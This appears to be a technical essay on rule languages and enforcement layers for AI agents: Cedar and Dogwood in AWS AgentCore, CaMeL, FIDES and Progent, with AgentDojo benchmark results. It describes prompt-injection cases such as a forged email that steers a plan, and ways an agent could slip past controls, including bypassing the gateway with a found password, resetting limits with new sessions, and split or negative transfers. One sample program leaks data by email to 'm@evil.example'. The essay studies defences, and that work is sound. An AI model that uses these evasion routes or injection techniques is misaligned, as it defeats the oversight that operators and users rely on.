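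The speed of the analysis is more important. Cutler and colleagues rewrote each application's rules and checked whether the new version allowed exactly the same requests. Translating and solving each check took 75.1 milliseconds on average, so a team could run one after every edit. These rule sets were small, though, while AWS says AgentCore accepts up to 200 KB of rules for a single resource.

### What Amazon has proved and what it only tests

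Disselkoen and colleagues describe two versions of Cedar. The first is a 1,673-line model in Lean, a language for writing both programs and proofs about them. They proved that in this model a matching `forbid` rule always overrides any `permit` rule, that no request succeeds without a matching `permit` rule, and that every function terminates. The second version, which customers use, has more than 15,000 lines of Rust, a general-purpose language. To check that the two versions give the same results, the team runs millions of randomly generated rules and requests through both every day.

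Cedar's developers found four bugs in the validator while working on the proofs, and 21 bugs in various parts of Cedar by testing. One of the four could make the validator run forever on certain inputs, even though Cedar's rules themselves can't loop endlessly. Random tests had little chance of finding this bug because very few inputs triggered it, and the team lists it among nine that testing missed. In another of the nine, the Rust engine checked group membership incorrectly, which could affect any rule that depends on who belongs to which group. The developers have fixed all of these, but the list shows that millions of matching answers in tests don't prove the code correct.

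In 2024, the proof that the translation into formulas was sound and complete existed only on paper. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) reports that Lean has now checked proofs for five kinds of analysis. These analyses determine whether a set of rules denies every request, whether it allows every request, whether one set allows everything another does, whether two sets are equivalent, and whether two sets have no allowed request in common. The comparison of the two refund rules uses the third kind. Proving the components shared by these analyses took 505 hours and nearly 22,000 lines, but proving the five analyses then took only seven hours. One shared component, which the earlier work lacked, turns the solver's answer into a valid Cedar request.

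Torlak ran a demonstration tool on eight sample applications published by Cedar's developers. In three of them, it found rules that might be mistakes because they were redundant or another rule made them pointless. Even people who know the language well evidently write rules that don't do quite what they seem to.

Several parts still have no proof. The analysis assumes that the SMT solver's answers are correct. AWS translated the analysis programs into Rust for its commercial service, and it tests the translations daily against the Lean versions. The Rust engine that decides real requests is also only tested, and in 2024 the parser that reads the rules had no Lean model. The proofs therefore connect the formulas only to the Lean model, and AWS relies on tests to connect that model to production. AWS overstates the case in *Introducing Cedar Analysis* when it claims that its proofs ensure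 the results "exactly match how your policies will behave in production".

*Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints* (2026) makes this criticism and proposes an alternative that generates the enforcement code from the specification and proves that the two correspond. Matra similarly generated the Ada code for Line 14 from proved models. The paper states that its language can express less than Cedar. For the shop, a mistake in its own rules is probably a bigger danger than an undiscovered bug in Cedar's engine, but an engine bug could affect every customer at once.

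### The same rule in Rego or Python

Rego can express more than Cedar, letting users define their own ways of combining rules and search through complex data. Cutler and colleagues say its worst-case running time is exponential, so decisions may be slow but do finish. Rego is based on the logic language Datalog, and no algorithm can determine for every pair of Datalog programs whether they are equivalent. Rego users therefore have no general way to check whether an edit has changed a policy's decisions. Meyer and Ritchie's loop programs have the same limitation.

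Python is much more expressive still. A Python check could look up the order in the shop's database, multiply the quantity by the unit price and ask the delivery company whether the kettle arrived. It could also hang, change the data it was supposed to check, or give different answers to the same request. AWS argues that such languages are too difficult to analyse, which is true in general but not of every program. The example refund rule could be written in three lines of Python without a loop, and a tool could translate them into the same formula. But the shop would need to find or build that tool, and it would lose the assurance that the rule will still be analysable after the next edit. As with C in aircraft, a team could recover much of that assurance by restricting how it uses Python and running a checker.

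### What a rule can't see

The refund rule denies refunds to customers who change their minds, but the reason for each request comes from the model, which relies on the customer's word. Nothing in the request shows whether that reason is true or what the refund is really for.

The user's identity is more reliable. AWS points out that details such as a customer's membership level come from the signed token, which the model can't alter. But these details can be out of date. If the shop never removed a former manager from its records, a rule for managers will still allow that person's requests.

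Other data that looks equally reliable may come from the model. One of AWS's examples forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order date, but the rule reads that date from the arguments of the call. If the model supplies a date from last week for an order from last year, the rule doesn't block the refund, although AWS writes that Cedar will always deny refunds after 90 days.

The most basic refund rule, that nobody gets back more than they paid, has the same problem. According to AWS's documentation, rules in AgentCore can read the arguments of the call, and AWS's *Policy authoring guide* also lists the current time. Together with the user's identity, these are enough to enforce a fixed limit, but they don't include the price in the shop's order records. The model could pass the price as another argument, but it would then control both numbers in the comparison. A shop that runs Cedar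 inside its own application can supply the price directly from its database. If it uses the gateway instead, it can leave this check to the refund tool.

Cedar also keeps no record of earlier requests. It treats a second refund for the same kettle just like the first, and an agent can get around the 100-euro limit by refunding 200 euros in two halves. An application can supply a record of earlier refunds with each request, and AgentCore now also accepts a language called Dogwood that can take earlier actions into account.

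### Calls that don't go through the gateway

According to AWS, the rules apply to "all tool traffic routed through the Gateway". An agent that finds the payment provider's password can therefore still bypass Cedar, although AWS describes the gateway in the same article as a checkpoint that the model can't circumvent. This is a realistic concern because Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes Claude models working around restrictions and taking unintended actions on real websites.

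Complete mediation therefore depends on how the shop sets up its systems. Only the refund tool should hold the payment password, the tool should accept calls only from the gateway, and the agent should have no other way to reach the payment provider. The agent must also be unable to edit the rules or detach them from the gateway. Cedar's analysis can't establish any of this because it examines only the rules, not the shop's network, passwords or staff accounts.

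## Dogwood: rules about sequences of actions

Cedar evaluates only the current request, so an agent can do a lot of harm through steps that are each allowed. AWS's *Securing AI agents with temporal policies in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) gives three examples. One agent looks up a customer, makes up a different account number and sends the money there. Another makes dozens of trades in a loop and exceeds a risk limit that no single trade would break. A third approves an insurance claim and denies it seconds later.

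In August 2026, AWS released Dogwood, an open-source language for such cases. Every Cedar rule is also a valid Dogwood rule, but Dogwood adds a second kind of condition, marked `when temporal`, that depends on what the agent has already done.

AgentCore keeps a history of events for this purpose. A `request` event contains the arguments of a tool call, and a `response` event also contains what the tool returned. An `error` event means the rules blocked the call or the tool failed. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls*, Dogwood's interpreter evaluates each temporal condition against the history and passes the result to Cedar as an extra field in the request, and Cedar then decides as usual.

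### Looking back through a history

This rule stops the agent from refunding the kettle twice. It follows a pattern in AWS's *Authoring temporal policies*, with some names shortened and one compulsory field left out:

```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when temporal {
  exists (n: Long).
    (count for (t: Timepoint). where
      (formerly within 24h
        (Action::"refund"::request{ input.order: context.input.order }
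         && tp(t)))) == n
    && n > 1
};
```

`context.input.order` is the order number in the current request, and `input.order` is the order number in a recorded one. The rule counts the refund requests for this order over the past 24 hours and blocks the call if there is more than one. The history already includes the current request, so n is 1 on the first attempt and 2 on the second.

InfoQ lists four main operators, which check whether something happened within a period, count how often it happened, count how many different values it involved, and add up the values. All four are shorthand for formulas in metric first-order temporal logic. "Temporal" means that a formula can refer to earlier events, and "metric" means that it can measure the time between them. "First-order" means that it can include statements about "some" or "every" piece of data, such as an order number. The logic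 is much older than AI agents. *The MonPoly Monitoring Tool* (Basin, Klaedtke and Zălinescu, 2017) describes a program that checks system logs against formulas of this kind.

Another operator, `since`, can make a manager's approval good for only one refund:

```
!refund::response  since within 1h  approve::response
```

This condition holds if an approval completed within the past hour and no refund has completed since then. Apart from the one-hour limit, software can check it with a single bit, which it updates at every event by an equation that could come from a Lustre program:

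```
ok = approved or (not refunded and (false -> pre ok))
```

The approval makes `ok` true, and it is still true when the agent requests a refund. When that refund completes, `ok` becomes false, so the next refund needs a new approval. To enforce the one-hour limit, the software must also store the time of the latest approval. A running total takes more memory because the software has to keep each amount until it is too old to count.

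Evaluation can therefore slow down as the history grows, but it remains a routine calculation. AWS's *Temporal policies* also sets limits on the work: at most three temporal operators per rule, 25 temporal rules per policy engine, and periods of up to 24 hours.

### One history or every history

Analysing a rule is harder than applying it, because the analysis has to cover every possible history. This is still manageable if the rules depend only on the order of a few yes-or-no events. Each condition then needs only a little memory, so the rules form a finite-state machine, and the tools RATP uses for interlockings could prove properties of them. Rules that compare account numbers or amounts across events are much harder to analyse.

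The two-counter machine that ran in Lustre at one instruction per tick shows why. Suppose an agent has a tool called `step` that takes three numbers, the machine's current instruction and its two counters. The rules permit a call only if its numbers are the machine's next state after the latest completed call. After (2, 1, 1), for example, they permit only (1, 0, 1). Checking a call takes one look-up and a few comparisons. But if the numbers can be of any size, no algorithm can determine, for every such set of rules, whether they will ever permit a call starting with 3, the stopping instruction. Such an algorithm could also determine whether any two-counter machine halts, which is impossible.

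Removing arithmetic from the language alone wouldn't fix this. Metric first-order temporal logic includes ordinary first-order logic, which Alonzo Church and Alan Turing independently proved undecidable in 1936. Dogwood uses only a subset of the temporal logic, and some subsets are decidable. Real services have limited numbers and memory, but this rarely helps in practice, as with flight computers.

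InfoQ reports that Cedar's automated analysis doesn't support temporal conditions, and that AWS created a separate language for this reason. Dogwood users therefore choose between a more expressive rule and one they can analyse each time they write a rule. The shop can find out in a fraction of a second exactly which additional requests a change to its 100-euro limit would allow, but it has no such tool for its rule against refunding an order twice.

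The examples in AWS's article on temporal policies show how much this matters. They are seven rules for an imaginary agent that trades on behalf of private-banking clients, and several do not do what the article claims:

- One rule should cap trades at $60,000 in total, but it adds up a cost field from price look-ups instead of trades.
- Another should restrict trades to the client's own portfolios, but it never checks the portfolio number.
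- A third should stop the agent from trading if its human adviser has been away for 15 minutes. It says `unless` where it should say `when`, so it permits trades only after the adviser has been away for that long.

The rules also fail in combination. All seven are `permit` rules, and a request needs only one matching `permit` to be allowed. One of them permits any trade under $25,000, so the agent could make any number of trades worth $24,999, whatever the other rules require. The spending cap should have been a `forbid` rule, as it is in AWS's documentation.

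A fairly simple analyser could find this last mistake without modelling time. It could treat every temporal condition as an unknown yes or no, then check whether the rules allow a $20,000 trade when all the answers are no, which they do. This method would sometimes raise false alarms. For example, if one rule required an approval within 30 minutes and another required one within an hour, the analyser would include the impossible case in which only the first condition holds. It would be less precise than Cedar's analysis but much better than no analysis.

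Other companies also want both features. The chip company NVIDIA is adopting Cedar for OpenShell, which runs agents in restricted environments. The reasons given in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell* (Raman, 2026) are decidable comparison of policies, an open standard and a path to temporal policies.

AWS has returned to analysis with Greenlight, a service it released as a preview in December 2026. According to *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026), the service flags conflicting rules and finds ways for an agent to reach resources outside its approved access. Pogorelec doesn't say whether the analysis covers temporal conditions. Greenlight also shows which recorded calls a proposed change would block. This check works for any rule that software can evaluate, but it only tests recorded histories.

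### Three transfers at once

Suppose a rule limits transfers to $5,000 in total, and an agent sends three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment. In an example from AWS that InfoQ relays, the result depends on whether the rule adds up `response` events or `request` events:

| Transfer | Total by responses | Decision | Total by requests | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| First | $0 | Allow | $2,000 | Allow |
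| Second | $0 | Allow | $4,000 | Allow |
| Third | $0 | Allow | $6,000 | Refuse |

The first version allows $6,000 in transfers, and the second allows only $4,000. AgentCore checks one request at a time in each session, but this doesn't fix the first version, because a response appears only after the transfer has finished. If the agent sent 30 transfers together, the first version could allow all $60,000.

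The first version can also fail when the transfers come one after another. When the agent requests the third transfer, that transfer has no response yet, so the total is $4,000 and the rule allows it. A rule based on responses would need to add the current amount to the total, and even then it would fail when transfers overlap.

The one-time approval has a similar weakness. If the agent requests two refunds before either completes, the condition holds for both, so one approval can cover two refunds. Checking for `refund::request` instead of `refund::response` would be worse, because the current request would count against itself and the rule would never permit a refund. If each approval applies to a particular order, the shop can prevent the second refund by also using its rule against refunding an order twice, because that rule counts requests.

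Counting requests has drawbacks too. If the payment provider is down on the first attempt, the shop's rule blocks a retry for 24 hours. AWS's explanations also conflict on whether refused attempts count. The documentation says AgentCore records a `request` event for each "authorized request", while AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* says refused attempts count too. Suppose the agent asks to transfer another $500 after the third transfer is refused. The total is $4,500 on the first reading and $6,500 on the second, so the transfer would be allowed only on the first.

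Negative amounts are a more serious problem. AWS's example of a cumulative budget adds up whatever whole numbers the requests contain. If an agent asks to transfer −$10,000, the payment tool will probably reject the request, but the history still contains it. The total is now −$10,000, so the agent can transfer $15,000 under a $5,000 limit. Cedar's analyser could reveal that the shop's refund rule allowed negative amounts without anyone asking about them, but with a temporal rule, somebody has to think of the possibility.

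### A new session starts a new count

AgentCore keeps a separate history for each session, and the caller names the session, so a caller can reset every count and total by choosing a new name. AWS's documentation warns that a limit on such a count or total is "not a security control against a determined caller". Its article on temporal policies nevertheless claims that an agent can't bypass them whatever it does. This is true only if software outside the agent's control chooses the session, because an agent that can write its own requests to the gateway can also start a new session.

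Even an honest agent can refund the kettle twice if the customer asks on Monday and again on Wednesday, because AgentCore deletes events after 24 hours. The shop also can't use these rules to limit its total refunds across all customers, because each user has a separate history even if their sessions have the same name. Adding or updating a temporal rule ends all open sessions, and new ones start with an empty history, so an agent that had nearly reached its limit would get a fresh allowance.

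The shop could make the limits stricter by using one long session per customer per day. But AWS recommends short sessions, because a session can handle only one authorization request at a time.

AWS acknowledges that no rewording of a rule can make it cover several sessions, so the shop needs another way to enforce limits that must always hold. It could have the refund tool mark an order as refunded in the order database before sending the money, and refuse any order already marked. This would work across all sessions and for any length of time, although somebody would have to deal with orders that were marked but never refunded. Dogwood would still be useful for rules about a single conversation, such as a ban on emailing anyone outside the company after the agent has read confidential files.

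Temporal rules also enlarge the trusted computing base. InfoQ notes that Dogwood relies on accurate timestamps, genuine events and durable storage. A Cedar rule with a fixed limit on the amount doesn't depend on any record of earlier calls. If the event log loses the record of a refund, a correct Dogwood rule can still allow a second refund.

### Rules written by a language model

Few people in a shop's finance department could write the rule against double refunds in Dogwood, so AWS offers a tool that uses AI to translate rules from plain English. It splits a document into individual rules, sets aside those that Dogwood can't express, and translates the rest. A conventional program then checks each translation. If it finds errors, the tool tries again, up to a fixed number of times.

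Some rules are set aside because the gateway can only allow or refuse a call, so it could enforce "no refund without approval" but not "pay every approved refund within 14 days". In *Real-time Policy Enforcement with Metric First-Order Temporal Logic*, Hublet, Basin and Krstić study more powerful enforcers, which can cause some actions as well as suppress others. The rules these enforcers can enforce still depend on which actions they control.

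The automatic check on a translation confirms that the rule is well formed and that every name in it exists. As AWS says, it doesn't confirm that the rule means what its author intended. The gateway applies the rule as written, so it may enforce the wrong policy. For instance, "refunds of $2,500 or less" becomes `amount <= 2500`, but if the refund tool counts in cents, the limit is actually $25. "Three refunds per hour" could mean three for each customer or three for each account, and the translator may choose the wrong one.

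AWS gives no figures for how often its translations are right, and even a small error rate would matter for a large set of rules. LoanLogics, which sells technology for auditing mortgages, wants to use Greenlight to check that its agents follow thousands of policies, according to Pogorelec. If a language model translated 3,000 rules and got 99% of them right, 30 would be wrong. People would soon notice the ones that blocked legitimate work, but they might not notice the ones that allowed something they shouldn't until an agent did it.

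People therefore have to review the translations, but Dogwood is hard to read, as the mistakes in AWS's trading example suggest. Concrete cases are easier to judge. The AWS article lists the decisions each rule should give, such as allowing a trade three minutes after the adviser last interacted with the agent. Running the rule with the misplaced `unless` on that case by itself would have exposed the mistake, because the rule would have refused the trade. A language model could also propose test cases, but they might repeat any misunderstanding it had of the requirement.

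### A classifier inside a rule

The decision itself can also depend on a learned model. *Customizable Runtime Enforcement for Safe and Reliable LLM Agents* (2025) describes AgentSpec, a language whose rules can require a language model to reconsider a risky action before an agent takes it. Rules in AgentCore can call one of Amazon's classifiers to check free text. In AWS's example, a bank's rule uses a classifier to reject any dispute whose description contains a US Social Security number.

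The classifier gives a confidence score, and the rule refuses the request if the score is at least 0.2. The gateway can guarantee that comparison, but it can't guarantee that every Social Security number gets a score that high. A number with its digits written as words might score lower, for example. The rule depends on the classifier just as the taxiing monitor depended on TaxiNet's estimates.

AWS doesn't report the classifier's accuracy in this example either, so suppose it flags 95% of descriptions that contain a Social Security number and 2% of those that don't. If 100 of 10,000 descriptions contain one, the rule blocks 95 of them and lets five through, and it also blocks 198 harmless descriptions. A lower threshold would let fewer Social Security numbers through but block more harmless descriptions.

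The bank also needs to know what happens when the classifier is unavailable. Cedar ignores a `forbid` rule that fails with an error. If AgentCore treated a failed classifier call the same way, it would accept the description without checking it.

An agent can improve its chance of getting a refused description through by repeatedly rewording it. If each version had an independent 5% chance of passing, the chance of at least one success in 20 attempts would be 64%. A rule with a temporal condition could count recent `error` events for disputes and refuse further attempts after the third. This would reduce the chance to 14%, provided the agent can't start a new session.

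## CaMeL: a restricted interpreter for an agent's plan

A Cedar rule can check the order date in a refund request, but not whether that date came from the shop's database or a customer's email. This matters because of prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in text that a language model will read, such as an email or a web page. The model may then follow them as if they came from its user.

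CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, tracks where every value an agent uses came from. Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). They built on developer Simon Willison's proposal to split an agent between two language models, so that the one choosing actions never reads untrusted text.

### Planning before reading

*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how CaMeL works. A planning model sees the user's request and writes a program in a subset of Python. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools, but the planner doesn't see the untrusted data they return. When the program needs a model to read that data, the interpreter passes it to a quarantined model, which has no tools and can only return a value in the format the program specifies, such as an email address.

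The interpreter labels every value with its sources and with the people who may read it, and a value computed from others inherits their labels. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy that checks the arguments and their labels, then allows the call or blocks it and returns a reason.

Suppose the shop's owner tells the agent to send the March accounts to the address in the latest email from Maria, the accountant. The planner might write:

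```
email   = get_latest_email("Maria")
address = ask_quarantined("Where should the accounts go?", email, EmailAddress)
doc     = get_file("march-accounts.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=doc)
```

An attacker has forged the latest email, which tells the agent to delete the shop's files and send the accounts to Eve. The files are safe, because the plan contains no call that deletes anything and the planner never reads the email. But the quarantined model may well return Eve's address, and the plan would then send Eve the accounts. Stopping this takes a policy such as:

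```
def check_send_email(to, attachment):
    if is_trusted(to) or to in readers(attachment):
        return Allowed()
    return Denied("The recipient has no access to this file.")
```

An address that the owner typed into the request counts as trusted, but one extracted from an email doesn't. The result therefore depends on who already has access to the file:

| Address found in the email | Already has access? | Result |
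|---|---|---|
| Maria's usual address | Yes | Sent |
| Eve's address | No | Refused |
| Maria's new address | No | Refused |

CaMeL can't distinguish Eve from Maria with a new address. In both cases an unfamiliar address came from an email, so the owner has to decide.

### What the limits on Python contribute

According to Nikolaou and colleagues, plans consist of assignments, tool calls, if/else branches and loops. The interpreter rejects arbitrary `while` loops and uncontrolled `break` statements. Plans can also define simple data classes, which specify the form of the quarantined model's answers.

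These limits remove the most obvious way to write an endless program, but they don't prove that every plan terminates. In ordinary Python, this loop runs until the computer is out of memory:

```
for item in items:
    items.append(item)
```

CaMeL's planner sometimes writes code that modifies lists. Whether this loop would run forever depends on the interpreter, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) point out in *The LLMbda Calculus* that CaMeL's language has no formal definition apart from its implementation. As with Meyer and Ritchie's loop programs, even a plan that is guaranteed to end can take too long, so operators still need a time limit.

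The policies are Python functions, which makes them easy to write. But unlike with Cedar, there is no general way to check whether an edit to a policy has changed its decisions. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025), a paper by two researchers at a security company, predicts that organisations with hundreds of tools will end up with inconsistent policy code, and recommends a declarative language such as Rego instead.

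CaMeL's guarantee comes mainly from planning before reading and from tracking the data. Even if plans could contain `while` loops, an email couldn't add a tool call to a plan that the planner had already written. Garby and colleagues provide stronger evidence with LLMbda, a language that allows unlimited recursion and lets programs ask a model for new code and run it. Every value carries a label, as in CaMeL. They gave a computer-checked proof that secret inputs can't affect public outputs except through whether the program finishes. So a Turing-complete language can have this guarantee if the tracking is right.

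The simplicity of plans is useful because a tool can check them before they run. CaMeLoT, which Nikolaou and colleagues built on top of CaMeL, translates each plan into a finite-state machine and gives it to a model checker. After each pass through a loop, the checker covers both stopping and continuing, so it accounts for any number of passes but raises some false alarms. The same method would work for `while` loops, so the absence of `while` loops probably helps less than the fact that plans are short and name their tools openly. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports that CaMeL's plans average 52 lines and five tool calls on a standard benchmark.

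CaMeLoT could express 22 of the 28 tool policies written for that benchmark. The others depend on facts known only at run time, such as who has access to a file. CaMeLoT can also check the order of actions, for instance that a security agent never disconnects a computer before a person approves it. Nikolaou and colleagues chose seven rules that CaMeL can't naturally express and wrote a faulty plan that breaks each one. CaMeLoT caught all seven faulty plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. Because of how they chose the rules, the test shows what the extra check makes possible but not how often it would matter.

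### A plan that obeys the file

Limits on the language also don't stop the planner from handing control to an attacker. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on a task that asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner couldn't see the file, so it sometimes wrote a loop with a branch for every tool. In simplified form:

```
for step in steps_in_file:
    if step.tool == "send_money":
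        send_money(step.recipient, step.amount)
    if step.tool == "update_password":
        update_password(step.password)
```

This plan has no `while` loop and finishes when it reaches the end of the file. But it is a small interpreter that runs the file as its program, so anyone who can edit the file can choose which tools run and with what arguments. An attack succeeded this way in two runs with the policies switched off.

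CaMeL's promise about the plan still held in those runs, because the plan already contained every tool call. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) uses the term "branch steering" for data selecting which of a plan's existing branches runs, and its definition of a secure plan explicitly allows this. That definition offers little protection when the plan contains every tool. Sassaman and colleagues' advice about network inputs applies here too, since a file that can select any action gives its author far more power than one that only supplies an amount.

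### Gaps in the tracking

Garby and colleagues also found ways for labels to go missing. In this program, the account balance is secret:

```
a = True
b = True
if balance > 10000:  a = False
if a:                b = False
if b:                send_email("m@evil.example", "rich")
```

If the balance is 20,000, `a` becomes false and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips the next assignment, so `b` stays true, keeps its public label, and the program sends the email. If the balance is 5,000, `b` becomes false and the program sends no email. Whoever owns the address can therefore learn whether the balance is above 10,000, although CaMeL would have refused an email sent directly under the first condition. The leak occurs because CaMeL updates labels only on the branch it takes.

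The planner never sees the attacker's text and would have to write this odd program itself, so this is better evidence that the tracking is unsound than that an attack is likely. More worryingly, they also found that CaMeL treated untrusted values as trusted once a plan had inserted them into a longer piece of text. If a planner wrote `to=f"{address}"` instead of `to=address`, a harmless choice of style in Python, the policy might let Eve's address through.

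Information can also leak through software outside the interpreter. If a plan fails, CaMeL asks the planner for another one, and each new attempt starts without the labels from the last. Whether a policy blocked the previous attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

Labels can also disappear between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. One agent read the applicants' records from a database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the records to an outsider. The coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the agent that sends messages. That agent's planner treated the whole request as coming from its user and added the email to its plan. The system leaked the data even though each agent had kept its own guarantee. The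 researchers' remedy is to pass untrusted values between agents as separate variables that the next planner can't read.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

AgentDojo, the benchmark used in most of these tests, simulates an office workspace, a bank, a Slack team and a travel service. It has 97 ordinary tasks, and it plants attacks in the data that the agent's tools return. Researchers count how many tasks the agent completes and how often the attacks succeed.

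Tallam and Miller give CaMeL's original completion rate as 67%, but that figure comes from early 2025 and models have improved. Two groups have since rerun CaMeL. Garby and colleagues tested the 16 banking tasks three times each and paired every task with nine attacks. Nikolaou and colleagues ran all 97 tasks without attacks.

| Tasks | Model | Policies | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
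| Banking | GPT-5.2 | Off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| Banking | GPT-5.2 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| Banking | MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| Banking | MiMo-v2.5 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| All four areas | Claude Haiku 4.5 | On | 49 of 97 | Not tested |

Planning before reading evidently stops most of these attacks by itself. About two thirds of the banking attacks needed a tool that would normally never appear in the plan. Turning on the policies stopped the few attacks that still succeeded, but also nearly halved the number of completed tasks. Banking is a hard case because several of its tasks involve acting on the contents of a file, which the policies are meant to prevent.

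The five successes in 622 attacks probably understate the risk of running without policies, because AgentDojo's attacks are fixed texts. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) used a language model to keep rewriting attacks according to whether they worked. One detector of injected text blocked every fixed attack but let through 28% of the rewritten ones. An attacker who could adapt to CaMeL would concentrate on the values that the quarantined model returns.

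Planning ahead makes agents complete fewer tasks, even without policies. Peters-Gill and colleagues compared agents with and without CaMeL on 112 industrial maintenance tasks, using five models. CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Most failures occurred because a step that wasn't in the plan turned out to be necessary halfway through the task.

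In the same study's multi-agent version of AgentDojo, giving each agent CaMeL cut the average rate of successful attacks from 12.9% to 0.2%. With separate variables for untrusted values, no attack succeeded. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks without any defence, so on this benchmark CaMeL could only reduce the number of tasks it completed. Attacks written specially for the model might still succeed.

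CaMeL also requires more computation. Tallam and Miller estimate that using two models roughly doubles the number of model calls, and that a task in which the quarantined model reads ten emails could take more than ten seconds. Their estimate does not cover token use.

### FIDES and Progent

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes Microsoft's FIDES, which also labels data but has no plan language. The model chooses one tool call at a time, so it can adapt to earlier results. When a tool returns untrusted data, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model extract something from it. It can also read the contents itself, but policies may then block consequential actions such as payments.

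The design also lets a policy allow the agent to act on the quarantined model's answer if that answer can only be yes or no. A single bit is too small to hold an attacker's instructions, although the attacker can still choose the bit. Costa and colleagues show that FIDES can prevent data from flowing directly to places the policies forbid, but it doesn't prevent information from leaking through the agent's choice of tools. For example, if the agent creates a calendar event only when an email asks for a meeting, anyone who can see the calendar learns something about the email.

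With GPT-4o, an ordinary agent completed about 82% of AgentDojo's tasks, and FIDES with policies about 52%. Attacks succeeded 152 times against the ordinary agent and never against FIDES with policies. However, the labels in this test were unusually good, because the researchers marked every field that an AgentDojo attack uses as untrusted. A company would have to work out which data an attacker could reach.

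*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) restricts the policy language instead. Its rules allow or forbid a tool call depending on the call's arguments, much as Cedar's do. A language model writes the rules for each task and proposes changes as the agent learns more. An SMT solver then compares the old and new rules. A change that only removes permissions takes effect automatically, while one that would permit any new call needs approval. Even an attacker who controls the model that writes the rules therefore can't expand the set of permitted calls without approval. This guarantee does depend on a restricted language, because the solver has to be able to compare any two sets of rules.

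Progent doesn't track where values come from, which matters in the example of the March accounts. At the start nobody knows the address, so the first rules might allow an email to anyone. After reading the forged email, the model might propose allowing emails only to Eve. This change removes permissions, so it would take effect without approval.

Progent reduced successful attacks on AgentDojo with GPT-4o from 39.9% to 1.0%, with little change in completed tasks. Ma and colleagues tested rewritten attacks against five defences that had stopped nearly all the fixed attacks on a GPT-4o-mini agent, and only Progent remained effective.

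| | What it restricts | What it guarantees | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | The plan, written before the agent reads untrusted data | Data can't add tool calls to the plan, and policies control where labelled data goes | 67% with policies off, 38% with them on (banking, GPT-5.2) |
| FIDES | What the agent may do after reading untrusted data | No direct flow of data that the policies forbid | 82% for an ordinary agent, 52% with FIDES (GPT-4o) |
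| Progent | The rules for tool calls | Permitted calls never grow without approval | Little change (GPT-4o) |

The completion rates come from different models and sets of tasks, so they don't show which design reduces task completion the least. It is probably Progent, because its requirements are the least strict. It permits any call that fits the rules, wherever the arguments came from.

### Bad plans, lies and reflexive approval

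All three designs trust the user's request. If the owner asks the agent to clear out old orders and the planner writes a program that deletes every order, CaMeL's tracking won't block it, because no untrusted data is involved. The request can also contain an attack, for example if the owner pastes in text from a phishing message. Ma and colleagues found that attacks succeeded much more often when the request was vague, naming no action and telling the agent to do whatever some text said.

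A policy can also allow actions based on false information. If a customer writes that a kettle arrived broken, the labels record that the claim came from the customer's message, but not whether it is true. A policy that blocks every refund based on such a message leaves the agent unable to handle complaints, while one that allows them will let some customers get refunds by lying.

Garby and colleagues ran into the same limit with an agent they wrote in LLMbda. Its plans can explicitly mark a piece of untrusted data as acceptable. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 75% of the banking tasks with its checks on, twice as many as CaMeL with policies. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request.

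The remaining cases go to the user, who might approve everything. In the test by Nikolaou and colleagues, CaMeL refused at least 17 of 97 tasks although there were no attacks. If it had asked the user instead of refusing, it would have asked in about one task in six, and the right answer would always have been yes. People soon stop reading such questions. Tallam and Miller suggest requiring the strictest approval only for actions that are irreversible or visible to outsiders, such as emails and payments.

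Progent asks for approval less often, since only 6% of its rule changes needed it on AgentDojo. With a simulated user who approved every change, 1.0% of attacks succeeded, and careful human review reduced that to zero. The rules written before the agent had read anything provided much of the protection, cutting successful attacks to 2.5% by themselves. But careful review requires the owner to check requests independently. If the agent asks whether to send the accounts to Maria's new address, the owner has to phone Maria, because the attacker may have written the email.

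## AI-written proofs about general-purpose code

Much of the case for restricted languages is that they make proofs less work. The seL4 proof took specialists years, while Cedar's analyser rechecks an edited rule automatically. In the autumn of 2026, AI systems did most of the specialist proof work for a large number of ordinary compiled programs. If proofs come to need little human labour for any program, a team has less reason to give up loops, pointers or other language features.

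### Checking a proof without trusting its writer

Proof assistants such as Lean and Rocq separate finding a proof from checking it. Here is a small but complete example in Lean, about a function that decides how much to refund:

```
def pay (asked price : Nat) : Nat :=
  if asked ≤ price then asked else price

theorem never_too_much (asked price : Nat) :
    pay asked price ≤ price := by
  unfold pay
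  split
  · assumption
  · exact Nat.le_refl price
```

The first two lines are the program. The next two state the theorem that the payment is at most the price, whatever the customer asks for. The last four are the proof, which replaces `pay` with its definition and splits the problem into two cases. If the customer asked for no more than the price, the function returns that amount, and the condition for this case is what needs proving. Otherwise the function returns the price, and the theorem holds because every number is at most itself.

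Lean expands these instructions into a fully detailed proof, and a small program called the kernel checks every step against a fixed set of logical rules. If an AI forgets the second case or invents a rule, the kernel rejects the proof and the AI tries again. Kleppmann (2025) argues in *Prediction* that writing proofs is one of the best uses for language models because it doesn't matter if they hallucinate.

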